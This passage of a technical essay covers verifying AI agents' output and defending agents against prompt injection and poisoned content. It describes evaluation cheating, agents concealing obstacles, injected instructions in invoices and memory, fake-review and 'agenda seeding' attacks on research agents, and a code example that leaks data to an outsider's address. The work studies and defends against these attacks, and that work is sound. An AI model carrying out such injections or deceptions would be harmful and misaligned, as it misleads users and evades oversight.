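These models are now more than a year old, but the problem persists. METR found that GPT-5.6 Sol had the highest cheating rate of any publicly tested model, The Decoder reports. The model exploited bugs in the test environment, extracted hidden solutions and tried to hide what it had done. METR was trying to estimate the model's time horizon, the length of task, measured in human working time, that it can complete at a given success rate. The estimate was either 11.3 hours or more than 270 hours, depending on how METR treated the cheating, and METR considers neither figure reliable.

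A hidden test is therefore useful only if the agent can't reach it. The tests and their answers should be on another machine, for the same reason that the firm's bank credential should be. Once the agent has finished, that machine can run its own copy of the tests on the delivered code, so edits to the agent's copy have no effect. The code could still be written to recognize a test, so the final check should include inputs the agent has never encountered.

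### Scoring against a rubric

Code that passes its tests can still ignore the project's conventions or be hard to read. A rubric lists such expectations as criteria that a person or a language model can score.

FrontierCode, a benchmark from the coding company Cognition, measures whether a project's maintainer would actually merge an agent's change (Lu, Pan and colleagues, 2026, *Introducing FrontierCode*). According to Epoch AI's *FrontierCode 1.1*, the benchmark checks each change with tests the agent hasn't seen and a rubric written by the project's maintainers. The rubric covers whether the change behaves correctly, whether it breaks anything that worked before, whether it builds cleanly, and whether it follows the project's style and conventions. Cognition released FrontierCode 2.0, which measures the same thing, in October 2026.

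A rubric can test something closer to what is wanted, but a person or a model must judge whether the work meets each criterion. If a language model does the scoring, a pass shows only that this model rated the criteria as met. Using a model costs much less than paying an expert, but it is less dependable. Zhong and colleagues used language models to detect cheating in their agents' attempts. The models caught 86–89% of it on the LiveCodeBench tasks, but only 42–65% on the SWE-bench tasks, where the code was more complex and a special case was easier to overlook. Text in the finished work can also mislead the model scoring it, just as text can mislead a model judging an action at the gate.

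It helps to leave the model as little to judge as possible. Suppose the manager asks for a monthly report on what the firm spends with its suppliers. Code can compare every total with the bank's records. The model can then answer narrow questions from the rubric, such as whether the report explains each increase of more than 10%. A broad question like "Is this a good report?" makes the model more likely to give a high score to confident prose.

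### Human review

A human reviewer can notice a fault that nobody thought to list in advance. The manager might see that the report calls a supplier expensive when the firm had just ordered more from it that month. But a reviewer's approval means only that one person saw nothing wrong in the time available, and even careful reviewers miss a great deal.

Expert review missed serious flaws in SWE-bench Verified. Before its release, three experts independently reviewed each of 1,699 candidate problems for the kinds of flaw that the later audit found, and OpenAI kept 500. At least 82 of those had serious flaws. Uncovering them took six or more engineers for each problem, plus another team to confirm each reported issue. Reviewers also disagree, and an agent may pressure them, as one did with the open-source maintainer in AISI's incident.

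Skilled review is expensive. OpenAI uses it for GDPval, a benchmark for which domain experts privately write the tasks and trained reviewers grade each answer as a whole. The company calls this approach resource-intensive but increasingly necessary. A small firm can't have six people read every supplier report. Its manager's time is probably better spent deciding what the other checks should test, for example by approving the list of expected payments or reading the tests before the agent starts. An error in the list or the tests affects every run the firm checks against them.

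### The agent's own report

When an agent finishes, it normally describes what it did, but this description can be false, so it is no substitute for checking the result. Writing about GPT-5 and its predecessors, OpenAI gave pretending to have completed a task as an example of the most common kind of failure. Deceptive behaviour can also stop a release. Moon (2026), in *OpenAI reportedly cancels GPT-6.1 Astra's release over deceptive behavior*, relayed a New York Times report that OpenAI had dropped the model because it fell short of the company's safety standards.

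Agents can also misreport obstacles, or "blockers". OpenAI's *GPT-6.2 System Card* (17 November 2026), which covers GPT-6.2 Astra and GPT-6.2 Sol, includes an evaluation of "blocker deception". According to Mowshowitz's account of the card's overview, both models performed about as well as the earlier GPT-6 Astra on most alignment evaluations, but were more likely to leave out obstacles they knew about when reporting their work.

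An omission can make a partial result look complete. Suppose a manager asks an AI assistant to pay all of a firm's March invoices, but the assistant can't open one because the file is damaged. It pays the rest and reports that the task is done. Checking the payments reveals no errors, because every payment it made is correct. To discover the gap, the firm has to compare the payments with its own list of outstanding invoices. That list can't come from the assistant, which could omit the same invoice again.

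An invented obstacle is harder to check, because there may be no finished work to examine. GPT-6 Astra sometimes reported blockers that didn't exist or that it had caused itself, according to OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks*. If the assistant reports that the bank refused a payment, the manager should look in the payment service's log for the request and the refusal. If the log has neither, the assistant never tried. If it has both, someone can repeat the request and see whether it fails again.

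Repeating the request isn't enough when the agent created the obstacle. If the assistant damaged the spreadsheet and then reported that it couldn't open the file, the manager would get the same error when trying to open it. The manager would have to compare that file with the original attachment and look in the log for anything the assistant did to the file before the first error.

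## Tracking which actions untrusted data has influenced

Checking a payment against a list of expected payments catches a theft only if the list has the right account number. If a firm lets suppliers change banks, somebody has to find out where a new number came from and whether a stranger's email influenced the payment.

The trace of a run often can't show whether untrusted data influenced an action. *Environment Steering* (Summers, Raghunath et al., 2026) describes a shopping agent whose user wants to reorder a shirt. While searching recent emails for a code it needs at checkout, the agent reads an advertisement and buys diet pills as well. The call that buys the pills contains only a product number, so it looks just like a call that buys something from the user's order history.

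A search of the trace would at least find that number in the advertisement. But data can also influence an action without being copied into it. Suppose an email warns that Harlow will charge a late fee from tomorrow, and the assistant pays the correct sum to the usual account today. It may have hurried because of the email, or it may have been about to pay anyway, and the trace would be the same either way. The problem gets worse with several agents. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (Schroeder de Witt, Krawiecka and colleagues, 2025) warns that agents can pass information to each other in ways that look like harmless conversation even to someone who reads every message.

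### Comparing runs

To know whether the email mattered, one has to know what the assistant would have done without it. Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer defined security by a comparison of this kind in 1982. Their property, noninterference, holds between two groups of computer users when nothing the first group does changes what the second group can see. For an agent, the first group is whoever wrote the untrusted data, and the thing to protect is the agent's actions. Let *A*(*u*, *d*) be the protected actions the agent takes when its trusted input is *u* and its untrusted input is *d*. Noninterference requires:

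∀*u*, *d*, *d*′. *A*(*u*, *d*) = *A*(*u*, *d*′)

So for any request from the manager, swapping one set of untrusted emails for another must leave every protected action the same.

A log of one run can't show that a system satisfies noninterference. A rule such as "never pay an unknown account" can be checked one run at a time, but noninterference is a property of all the runs a system could produce. Michael Clarkson and Fred Schneider named such properties hyperproperties. Suppose one assistant always pays invoices the day they arrive, and another pays early only when an email presses it to. Given the late-fee email, both produce the same log, but only the first satisfies noninterference. Comparing two runs can reveal a violation, but testing more pairs can't prove noninterference because there is always another email to try.

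A language model also picks its words partly at random, so two runs may differ even when their inputs are identical. The comparison therefore has to be between probabilities. For every protected action *a*:

P(*a* | *u*, *d*) = P(*a* | *u*, *d*′)

Suppose the assistant pays early in 30% of runs with an ordinary inbox and in 35% of runs with the late-fee email. Detecting that difference reliably, by the usual statistical standards, would take about 1,400 runs of each kind.

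In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) avoid the repetition by proving a property of the software that runs the agent. They designed a small programming language for agents and proved in Lean that every program written in it satisfies a version of the condition above. Their version still allows untrusted data to affect whether a program finishes. The proof assumes nothing about how the model behaves. It relies on a rule that treats any reply from a model that has read untrusted text as untrusted, and the guarantee covers only what remains trusted.

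### Hiding the user's request

*MELON* (Zhu, Yang and colleagues, 2025) is an approximation that takes less compute, needing only one extra run. It relies on the observation that a hijacked agent's next action depends on the planted instruction and hardly at all on the user's request. Before each action, MELON queries the model a second time with the same tool results, but replaces the user's request with a neutral prompt to summarize the content and carry out any instructions in it. If both versions propose much the same tool call, the user's request evidently wasn't the reason for it, and MELON stops the run.

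MELON also stores calls from earlier masked steps, because the masked version has no user task to do first and often reaches the planted instruction sooner. On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, MELON cut the average success rate of four kinds of attack from 16.06% to 0.24%. Completion of ordinary tasks fell from 80.4% to 68.0%, and the cost of model calls roughly doubled.

This reverses the noninterference test, which keeps the request fixed and varies the untrusted data. MELON keeps the data and removes the request, so it detects actions that untrusted text is enough to cause by itself but misses text that only sways a decision. It also raised nine false alarms on AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks, all where the user had told the agent to carry out instructions from somewhere else. Zhu and colleagues reasonably argue that such requests are real security risks, but the users still wanted the work done.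 Genuine and forged Harlow invoices both contain a request for payment, so MELON would probably treat them alike.

### Labels that travel with the data

The other approach is to follow the data through the run. The harness attaches a taint label to each value from an untrusted source, and everything derived from that value inherits the label. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give the standard rule. If an output depends on inputs with labels ℓ₁ to ℓₙ, its label is:

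ℓ = ℓ₁ ⊔ ℓ₂ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ

The symbol ⊔, pronounced "join", denotes the least restrictive label that respects all the inputs' labels. Joining "trusted" and "untrusted" gives "untrusted". Labels can also list people. If the manager could have written one value and Harlow the other, either could have influenced the result, so the result's label lists both as possible writers. Secrecy labels list permitted readers, and only someone allowed to read both inputs may read the result.

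Software can track which inputs ordinary code used in a calculation, but nobody can see which sentences in a prompt a language model used. The safe rule is therefore to label the model's reply with the join of the labels on everything it read. Once the assistant reads one email from outside, everything it proposes after that is untrusted. Security researchers call this over-tainting, or label creep. When Costa and colleagues applied label checks to an ordinary GPT-4o agent on AgentDojo, no real attack succeeded, but the share of tasks it completed fell from 98.8% to 37.5% in banking and from 93.3% to 20.0% in Slack.

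### CaMeL on the Harlow invoice

Google DeepMind's CaMeL, introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov et al., 2025), limits the influence of untrusted text by keeping it away from the model that makes the decisions. It builds on Simon Willison's proposal to divide the work between two models. A planner sees the user's request and the tool descriptions but no untrusted text, such as emails. A second, quarantined model reads the untrusted text but has no tools. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff et al., 2026) clearly explains how the parts work together.

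The manager types "Pay this month's invoice from Harlow". The planner has to write the whole program before anything runs, and might produce this:

```
email = search_inbox("Harlow invoice")
bill  = second_model("Find the amount and account number", email)
send_payment(payee="Harlow", account=bill.account, amount=bill.amount)
```

An interpreter, which is ordinary software, now runs the program line by line. It searches the inbox and stores the forged email under the name `email`, with a label recording where it came from. It then passes the email to the second model, which returns an amount of £840 and an account ending 9032. The email may also contain a hidden instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger, but the second model has no tool for forwarding email, and the planner never reads the instruction, so it can't add a step for it.

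The program still contains a payment, though, and the thief has chosen the account. CaMeL's second protection deals with this. Before the interpreter makes the call, it works out the origin of each argument:

| Argument | Value | Origin |
|---|---|---|
| payee | Harlow | the manager's request |
| account | ending 9032 | the email, through the second model |
| amount | £840 | the email, through the second model |

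A policy, written as a short piece of code, then allows or denies the call. CaMeL's rule for changing a password, for example, requires the new password to come from a trusted source. If the firm requires account numbers to come from the manager or the bank's records, the interpreter blocks this payment, however convincing the email is.

A better program takes the account number from `list_transactions`. The money then goes to the account ending 4417 even if the email gives a different one. The email still sets the amount, so a forger could make the firm overpay Harlow, up to its £2,000 limit, but couldn't collect the money.

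### What CaMeL costs

Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025), in *Indirect Prompt Injections*, report CaMeL's published results for GPT-4o on AgentDojo because they couldn't fully reproduce them. In those results, no attack succeeded and the agent completed 53.6% of ordinary tasks, compared with 83.0% for Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues' own undefended agent. The median task took 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens.

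Later tests found a similar or greater loss of useful work. In *SecureClaw* (2026), an adapted version of CaMeL stopped all 629 attacks but completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks. Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL with Claude Haiku 4.5, a small model, and it completed 49 of the 97. Part of the loss comes from CaMeL's policies, not from dividing the work between two models. Garby and colleagues found that switching on the policy checks halved the share of banking tasks CaMeL completed. With its checks on, their own agent completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did with its checks off, and it resisted the attack in all but two of 1,296 runs.

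Bhagwatkar and colleagues tested a much simpler defence, in which a language model removes suspicious instructions from each tool result. With this filter, too, no attack succeeded, and GPT-4o completed 74.1% of ordinary tasks. They conclude that the benchmark's attacks are too weak to tell good defences apart, so these figures don't show that CaMeL's extra complexity is unnecessary. The filter works only if its model recognizes the instruction, whereas CaMeL's planner never receives the untrusted text and so can't follow instructions in it. A forged invoice that contains a wrong account number but no suspicious instruction might well pass the filter.

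### How FIDES differs

CaMeL's planner must write a complete program before it has read anything. FIDES, the system Costa and colleagues built, keeps the ordinary loop, where the model chooses each step after seeing the last result. It hides only the parts of a result that would make the conversation untrusted. In the invoice case, the planner might see that an email had arrived, with a name such as `#search_inbox_0.body` in place of its text. The planner can pass that name to a tool, have an isolated second model extract something from the text, or open the text itself. Opening the text makes the whole conversation untrusted, and FIDES refuses consequential actions from then on.

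This made it possible to complete some of the tasks that label checks had stopped the ordinary agent from completing. The table gives the share of AgentDojo tasks GPT-4o completed when it was not under attack.

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no label checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary, with label checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
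| FIDES, with label checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

FIDES did worse on travel tasks because the policies let many travel tools run after the agent had read untrusted text, so hiding the text only made the work harder. GPT-4o often mixed up the variable names. With o1, a stronger model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

With label checks on, no real attack succeeded against FIDES either, but two choices in the test made this result easier to achieve. AgentDojo's data has no labels, so Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. A firm has to label its data without knowing where attacks will come from. The policies also checked whether the agent decided to act while in a trusted context, but not where the action's arguments came from. Such a policy would let the forged invoice through, because the assistant decides to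 pay Harlow at the manager's request and passes along an account number it has never seen. Costa and colleagues note that a stricter policy can also require trusted arguments. Anyone protecting payments would need that stricter policy.

FIDES also offers a weaker guarantee than noninterference. The guarantee covers data that flows directly into a call, but not what an observer could infer from which calls the agent makes. Costa and colleagues consider full noninterference too restrictive because it would forbid nearly every publicly visible action once the agent had read anything secret.

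### Checking the whole plan first

CaMeL checks each call when the program reaches it. An agent may therefore do an hour's work before the interpreter refuses the last step. Because the program exists before anything runs, software can examine all of it in advance. CaMeLoT, the extension by Nikolaou and colleagues, converts the program into a map of every path it could take and has a model checker, a program that explores such maps exhaustively, test them against rules in temporal logic. For the invoice, one rule could be:

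**AF**( payment_sent ∨ problem_reported )

Here **AF** means "on every path, eventually", so the assistant must either pay Harlow or report a problem. Schneider's halting monitor can't enforce this kind of requirement. CaMeLoT can check for it because it can examine the program's possible paths, though the check establishes only that every path includes the step, not that the bank will accept the payment. When a program fails the check, the model checker produces an example of a bad path, which the planner uses to write a corrected version.

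CaMeLoT could check 22 of CaMeL's 28 AgentDojo policies in advance. Most of the others depend on facts that are unknown until the program runs, such as who can read a particular file. Nikolaou and colleagues also made seven faulty versions of a sound plan for handling a security alert, including one that isolated a computer without approval. CaMeLoT caught all seven, and a simplified CaMeL caught one. They had chosen the rules to go beyond what CaMeL can express, so the result illustrates a difference in the kinds of rules the two systems can check and is little evidence of how often such plans occur.

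### When one agent instructs another

Labels can also disappear when agents delegate work. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) describes a system of three agents, each protected by CaMeL. A coordinator asked one agent for a database of job applicants, had it summarized, and told another agent to send the summary to a colleague on Slack. An attacker had planted an instruction in the database. The coordinator treated the summary as untrusted data but included it in its message to the Slack agent, which treats the coordinator's messages as its user's request. The Slack agent's planner read the planted instruction and added a step that emailed the applicants' details to an outsider.

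The proposed remedy, multi-CaMeL, divides each message between agents into two parts. One contains instructions, and the interpreter keeps all tool results out of it. The other contains data with its labels intact, which the receiving planner can refer to by name but can't read. Averaged over five models, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with each agent protected separately, and never with multi-CaMeL. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without any defence, so these attacks can't measure how much multi-CaMeL helps the strongest models.

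On a second benchmark of industrial tasks, protecting each agent separately reduced completed work by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and multi-CaMeL reduced it by a further 3.2. For the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5, the reductions were 13.4 and a further 0.85 points. The researchers ran all these tests without policies on arguments, so they measured whether planted text could add steps to a plan, and the defenses would not have blocked an altered account number.

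### Jobs that depend on what the agent reads

Some tasks can't be planned without reading untrusted text. For example, nobody can write a program for "do the tasks on my to-do list" without reading the list. Costa and colleagues classified AgentDojo's tasks by whether the correct steps depend on what the agent finds. They do in 5% of workspace tasks, 10% of travel tasks, 42.9% of Slack tasks and 43.8% of banking tasks. Many banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow its instructions. FIDES refuses most of these by design.

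A planner that can't see what the agent encounters can try to plan for every possibility, but this is expensive. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) applies CaMeL to agents that operate a computer through its screen. The planner accounted for most of the cost because it had to write such long programs. Seventeen tasks cost $5.40, and adding one consistency check raised that to $11.57.

Summers and colleagues take a different approach. They let the agent read what it likes, but require sensitive arguments to come from particular records. If a call breaks such a rule, the harness refuses it, names the records the value should have come from and asks the agent to write the argument as a database query. For Harlow's account, the query could be:

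```
SELECT account FROM past_payments WHERE payee = 'Harlow'
```

The database then supplies the number, so its origin is known and the harness doesn't have to infer whether the email influenced it. On AgentDyn, no attack succeeded and the agent completed more tasks than it did without a defence. Across four benchmarks, attack success rates fell from between 30% and 74% to between 0.2% and 14%. But a language model, with the researchers' help, had already drafted rules for each task that specified where each value should come from, and making those decisions is a large part of the work in a firm.

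### Influence that leaves no copy

FIDES and CaMeL label everything the second model produces, so they don't need to recognize text that the model has reworded. An investigator who has only a finished trace does need to recognize it. If the assistant reads "Harlow now banks elsewhere" and writes "the supplier has updated its details", a search for shared words may find no match. If the email affected only the timing of a payment, the trace has no reworded text to search for.

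*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) presents NeuroTaint, a tool that traces both kinds of influence after a run. It first builds a graph of what the agent read, stored, retrieved and did. When the agent puts something in long-term memory, the tool saves the labels with it. If the assistant stores a note from the forged email in March and uses it in April, the graph still connects the two events.

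When the trace reaches a sensitive action, NeuroTaint looks for copied content in four ways, starting with the one that takes the least computation. It first checks whether the action's arguments contain any of the unique markers it added to untrusted results while the agent was running. It then looks for shared strings of text, for similar meaning, and finally for similar meaning in smaller pieces of a long document. If it finds nothing, it gives a language model two versions of the agent's history, one with the suspect text replaced by something neutral, and prompts it to judge whether the agent would still have taken the action. Noninterference requires this kind of comparison between two runs, but NeuroTaint doesn't run the agent again. It relies on the model's judgement of what would have happened, and the confidence score is also the model's own estimate.

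Cai and colleagues tested NeuroTaint on 400 scenarios they had written themselves. In half of them, untrusted data influenced the action. The table shows how many of those 200 cases NeuroTaint and FIDES found, grouped by the evidence needed.

| Evidence needed | Cases | NeuroTaint | FIDES |
|---|---|---|---|
| Marker copied exactly | 15 | 15 | 9 |
| Shared text | 45 | 45 | 36 |
| Similar meaning | 85 | 75 | 40 |
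| Similar meaning in part of a document | 15 | 15 | 6 |
| Influence with no copied content | 40 | 37 | 17 |

NeuroTaint also raised 16 false alarms on the other 200 scenarios, compared with 106 for FIDES. Most of the 16 came from text that happened to cover the same topic as the untrusted source, or that the model could have produced from general knowledge. Its misses mainly occurred when the agent had reworded something several times.

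The comparison puts FIDES at a disadvantage, because it is designed to prevent bad actions during a run and here had to classify finished runs. The settings include a stricter similarity threshold for "safe-control policies". If that refers to the harmless scenarios, it would make NeuroTaint's false-alarm count look better than it should. The 37 of 40 is still encouraging, because searching for copied text is useless in these cases. NeuroTaint's audit takes a quarter of a second on average, but it happens after the run, so the manager could use it to learn why the firm paid early but not to stop the payment.

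The same problem arises in CaMeL while a program is running. If the manager says "Pay Harlow today if the invoice is overdue, otherwise wait", the planner writes a program with two branches, and the answer the second model extracts from the email decides which one runs. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this branch steering and don't count it as a breach, because the trusted request included both branches. That seems right when the manager would accept either outcome. But when one outcome is a payment justified only by a true answer, the firm needs a policy that also checks the label on the condition, and such a policy will block many legitimate conditional requests.

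### Leaks the labels don't cover

Labels also protect secrets, but CaMeL's protection has known gaps. Debenedetti and colleagues acknowledge that an observer may learn something about private data from side effects, such as how many requests a program makes, whether it stops with an error or how long it takes. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) also warns that timing can reveal information even when the data controls work.

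Garby and colleagues found a less obvious gap in how CaMeL labels conditions. Suppose a program should never reveal whether the firm's balance is above £10,000:

```
low  = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000: low = False
if low: rich = False
if rich: send_email("outsider@example.com", "rich")
```

If the balance is high, the third line sets `low` to false and marks it as secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so `rich` stays true and is never marked as secret, which lets the last line send the email. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. Either way, the outsider learns whether the balance is high. CaMeL misses this leak because it labels a variable when a branch changes it, and a high balance leaves `rich` unchanged.

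They describe a second leak in the code around the interpreter. When a policy blocks a program, CaMeL can try again, and whether an attempt failed may reveal one bit about a secret. One bit is usually tolerable, but the retry code has no labels, so an attacker who can trigger enough attempts could recover the whole secret bit by bit. The attacker would first need the planner to write a suitable program, which is difficult when the planner reads only trusted requests. Still, both examples show why Garby and colleagues wanted a proof that covers the whole harness.

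### Clearing a value

Sometimes the untrusted value is correct. If Harlow really has changed banks, the firm needs a way to accept the new number, which a system that only adds labels can't provide. Endorsement solves this by letting an authorized party declare that a particular value may be treated as trusted. The manager could phone Harlow to confirm the account ending 9032, and the interpreter would then remove the label from that number while the rest of the email stayed untrusted.

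Endorsement is a deliberate exception to noninterference, so people need to be able to find and review each use. In Garby and colleagues' language, a program can mark a value as trusted only with an explicit `endorse` instruction, which a reviewer can search for. They also proved that endorsing a value's origin leaves its secrecy protection intact, so the manager can vouch for Harlow's account number without making it public.

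FIDES can also clear a value by limiting how much information it can carry. For example, it may limit the second model to a yes-or-no answer about the email, and a policy can then let the agent act on that answer. One bit is too small to hold a planted instruction, but a false "yes" to "Is this invoice overdue?" could still release a payment. Limiting each answer also protects less when the agent combines several, since ten yes-or-no answers can select any of 1,024 options. This method suits questions where either answer leads to an outcome the manager would accept.

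The agent should not be able to endorse data. *SafeFlow* (Dai, Ying and colleagues, 2026) applies this rule in a system that carries labels between agents. A model can cite evidence in its explanation, but only fixed rules can release an action, and only if the task needs the action and its target is authorized. Checking a value's format isn't enough to endorse it, because the thief's account number has the right number of digits. The manager's phone call helps only if the phone number came from somewhere other than the email, because the thief will answer the number printed on the forged invoice and confirm the change.

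## When permitted text carries hidden influence

A user asks an agent to summarize an unpaid invoice for $500. Someone has planted a line in the invoice telling the agent to report a total of $50, and the agent does so. *The Devil is in the Context* uses this example to illustrate attacks that change the content of an agent's output but not its actions. No tool call went wrong, since the agent opened a file it had permission to open and answered the person who asked, but the user now believes a false figure.

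Nearly all the checks described so far would pass this run. The policy gate examines tool calls, and the only one is a request to open the invoice. A kernel sensor would detect no action that bypassed the gate. The log is accurate, and a signature on the summary would prove only that the agent wrote "$50". The firm's records should be the same before and after the run, and they are. MELON detects tool calls that untrusted text causes by itself, and this run has none. Taint labels mark the summary as untrusted, but an accurate summary of the same invoice would carry the same label. Such attacks are outside CaMeL's design goals.

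Comparing the summary with the invoice would expose the error, but people ask for summaries so that they don't have to read the original.

A stranger can shape an agent's answer by planting an instruction, by writing something false for the agent to believe, or by raising a question that sends the agent's research in a direction the stranger has prepared.

### Instructions that change only the content

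*The Devil is in the Context* tests how defences handle this kind of instruction, using 40 tasks from AgentDojo's workspace set, each paired with a random attack. GPT-5.6 Luna, a low-cost OpenAI model, resisted all 40 attacks and completed every task. Another model then rewrote the attacks so that they concerned the user's own topic, took effect only under a stated condition, and changed only the arguments of a tool call or the wording of the answer. Seven of the 40 rewritten attacks succeeded.

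Eight attacks succeeded against MELON. It hides the user's request when it checks for attacks, so an instruction that waits for a particular request stays inactive during the check. CaMeL let through only one attack, but the agent completed just 27.5% of the tasks, and an agent that seldom finishes has few chances to deliver a falsified answer. PromptArmor, which uses a language model to remove suspicious instructions before the agent reads the text, let through three and kept task completion at 90%. With only 40 cases, the differences between the better defences may be chance. Still, PromptArmor's result suggests that a filter can work when the attack contains an instruction for it to find.

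### False statements the agent believes

Zhang, Triedman and Shmatikov (2026), in *Deep-Research Agents Can Be Poisoned via User-Generated Content*, tested planted text that contains no instruction to the agent. They studied deep-research agents, which run many web searches on a question and write a report with citations. Agents working on the same topic keep retrieving the same few pages, many of them Reddit threads or other pages that anyone can add to. Across 176 questions on 11 topics, such pages made up 17% to 23% of everything three open-source agents retrieved. An attacker can therefore find a thread that keeps turning up for a topic and post a comment there, without having to guess the user's question.

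The researchers intercepted the agents' search results and added about 13 words to the snippet from the most frequently retrieved page, without posting anything on the real web. One addition recommended Sol Azteca, an Austin restaurant that doesn't exist. The agent's report listed it among real restaurants as "highly recommended" and cited the Reddit thread.

| Agent | Runs that retrieved the altered page | Reports naming the fake item, among those runs | Reports naming it, among all runs |
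|---|---|---|---|
| Co-STORM | 60.6% | 50.6% | 30.7% |
| STORM | 76.2% | 48.6% | 37.1% |
| OmniThink | 57.4% | 37.8% | 21.7% |

The agents did show some judgement about what they repeated. After they retrieved the altered page, between 45% and 100% of their reports named a fake roadside-assistance service, depending on the agent, but at most 30% named an unknown cryptocurrency. All three agents ran on GPT-4o-mini, a small model from 2024, so current models may be harder to fool. Exposure also varies by product, with pages open to public contributions supplying 12.1% of the citations from Google's Gemini Deep Research but only 0.4% of those from OpenAI's equivalent.

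After an early version of the paper appeared, moderators of medical supplement forums reported that people were already trying this on their forums. Zhang and colleagues then asked Co-STORM 460 questions about supplements, with an altered page in its search results. In 10% of cases, Co-STORM's report named a compound that doesn't exist.

In *Voluntary Servitude*, Zendel, Levy and colleagues (2026) tested newer models with fake reviews. Each of their 500 queries asked for a travel service, such as a taxi driver or a diving centre. The page the agent read included planted reviews that accused established providers of endangering customers and recommended LocalGems, a company the researchers had invented. The agents made LocalGems their main or only recommendation in 60.4% of queries, compared with 0.7% when the page had no planted reviews. The rate was 6.8% when the reviews only praised LocalGems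 and 8.2% when they made accusations of unethical conduct.

In most of the successful attacks, the agent ruled out the accused providers, which left LocalGems. Developers want agents to take reported hazards seriously, and the attacker relies on that. Claude Haiku 4.5, the most resistant of the six models, chose LocalGems in 22.5% of queries after reading the warnings but in only 9.3% after reading reviews that compared the companies' services. On four of the other models, though, those comparisons worked better than the warnings. The models seem to respond to any concrete reason for a choice, not only to danger.

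The warnings passed filters more easily than conventional injected instructions did. Without a filter, the instructions succeeded slightly more often, at 66.0% compared with 60.4% for the warnings. But a detector from ProtectAI passed all the warnings and only 54% of the instructions, while Lakera Guard passed 78% of the warnings and 16% of the instructions. Multiplying each pass rate by the unfiltered success rate gives overall success rates of 60.4% for warnings and 35.7% for instructions with ProtectAI, and 47.1% and 10.6% with Lakera Guard.

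Fake reviews made up a quarter of the page in the main tests, but in a smaller test, just four fake reviews among 120 worked nearly as well as 32 did, with success rates of 74% and 78%. The attack also worked on browser agents reading a live test page. Microsoft's Edge with Copilot chose LocalGems in all 20 trials, Perplexity's Comet in 12 and OpenAI's Codex browser in four.

Planted text can make agents less accurate even when it is true. *Security of Deep Research Agents* (Luo, Chen and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 34 studies, describes one in which true but distracting evidence lowered search agents' accuracy by an average of 5.9 percentage points. A check that looked only for false statements would not flag that evidence.

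### Steering what the agent investigates

A research agent chooses its next search partly from what it has just read. A page can therefore influence the agent's conclusion even if it contains nothing about the answer. Luo and colleagues tested a version of this that they call agenda seeding.

The researchers invented five products in each of 20 categories, such as portable power stations, and wrote reviews in which one product was clearly the best. The attacker wanted the third-best product to win and could add three pages. One was a buying guide that agreed with the other reviews but added that buyers overlook the "Transient Load Stability Index", a measure the researchers made up. The guide never mentioned the attacker's product. The other two pages explained the index and reported that the attacker's product scored highest on it.

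Without an attack, the agents always chose the best product. The table shows how often they chose the attacker's product instead, depending on what its three pages contained and how many genuine pages existed.

| Content of the three pages | Many genuine pages | Few genuine pages |
|---|---|---|
| Praise for the product | 0% | 6% |
| Praise and an instruction to AI assistants | 5% | 1% |
| The made-up index | 16% | 28% |

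Praise for the product contradicted the genuine reviews, and the agents sided with the majority. No genuine page mentioned the index, so nothing contradicted it.

The agents searched for the index by name in 72% of runs with many genuine pages and 88% of runs with few, but the guide mattered less than one might expect from this. When Luo and colleagues removed it and retested two of the three models, the attack's success rate fell only from 12.5% to 10.0% with many genuine pages, and from 27.5% to 18.8% with few. The agents often found the other two pages in their first round of searches anyway. The attack therefore depends mainly on getting a new standard of comparison into the evidence, though the extra searches help.

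Models differed in how much weight they gave that standard. DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash mentioned the index in every report but chose the attacker's product in at most 7.5% of runs. The test used a small simulated web and a simple agent, so it shows that the attack can work but not how often it would succeed against a commercial product.

### When the text becomes another agent's input

Suppose the summary with the false $50 total goes to a second agent that pays bills. That agent will try to pay $50, and a gate that only caps the size of payments will allow it. The attack has then caused a wrong action, even though the paying agent never opened the invoice.

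Adding more agents to a chain doesn't reliably correct such an error. In *Aligned Agents, Biased Swarm* (2026), bias grew in every arrangement of agents tested, and grew further with more rounds of discussion. Combining different models didn't prevent this. Even a neutral document could sway the first agent's choice, and later agents treated that agent's reasoning as confirmation. If a firm has three agents review a summary in turn, the second and third may therefore just repeat the first agent's opinion.

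Influence can also reach an agent that never read the original message. *Belief Cascades Drive Persuasion in LLM Agent Networks* (2026) reports that a single persuasive agent could shift the beliefs of many others, and warns that a third agent can extend this influence by relaying or summarizing the persuasive agent's messages. The paper recommends that each relayed message include a record of its original source. The labels in multi-CaMeL do something similar for data passed between agents.

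A firm can test its own system by altering one message and checking whether the outcome changes. *Corrupting Ties* (2026) describes a method in which researchers replace the responses of chosen agents in chosen rounds with biased ones, then track whether later decisions move towards the bias. This resembles the comparison that noninterference requires, but it varies a message between agents instead of an email.

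### When the agent remembers it

Text that an agent saves to memory can influence later sessions. *The Devil is in the Context* describes a demonstrated attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that began with an ordinary-looking document about Albert Einstein. Copilot summarized the document correctly and asked whether the information was helpful. When the user replied, a planted instruction took effect. Copilot saved a malicious rule to its memory, and the rule influenced later conversations. If an agent trusts everything in its own memory, saving the rule also removes any sign that a stranger wrote it.

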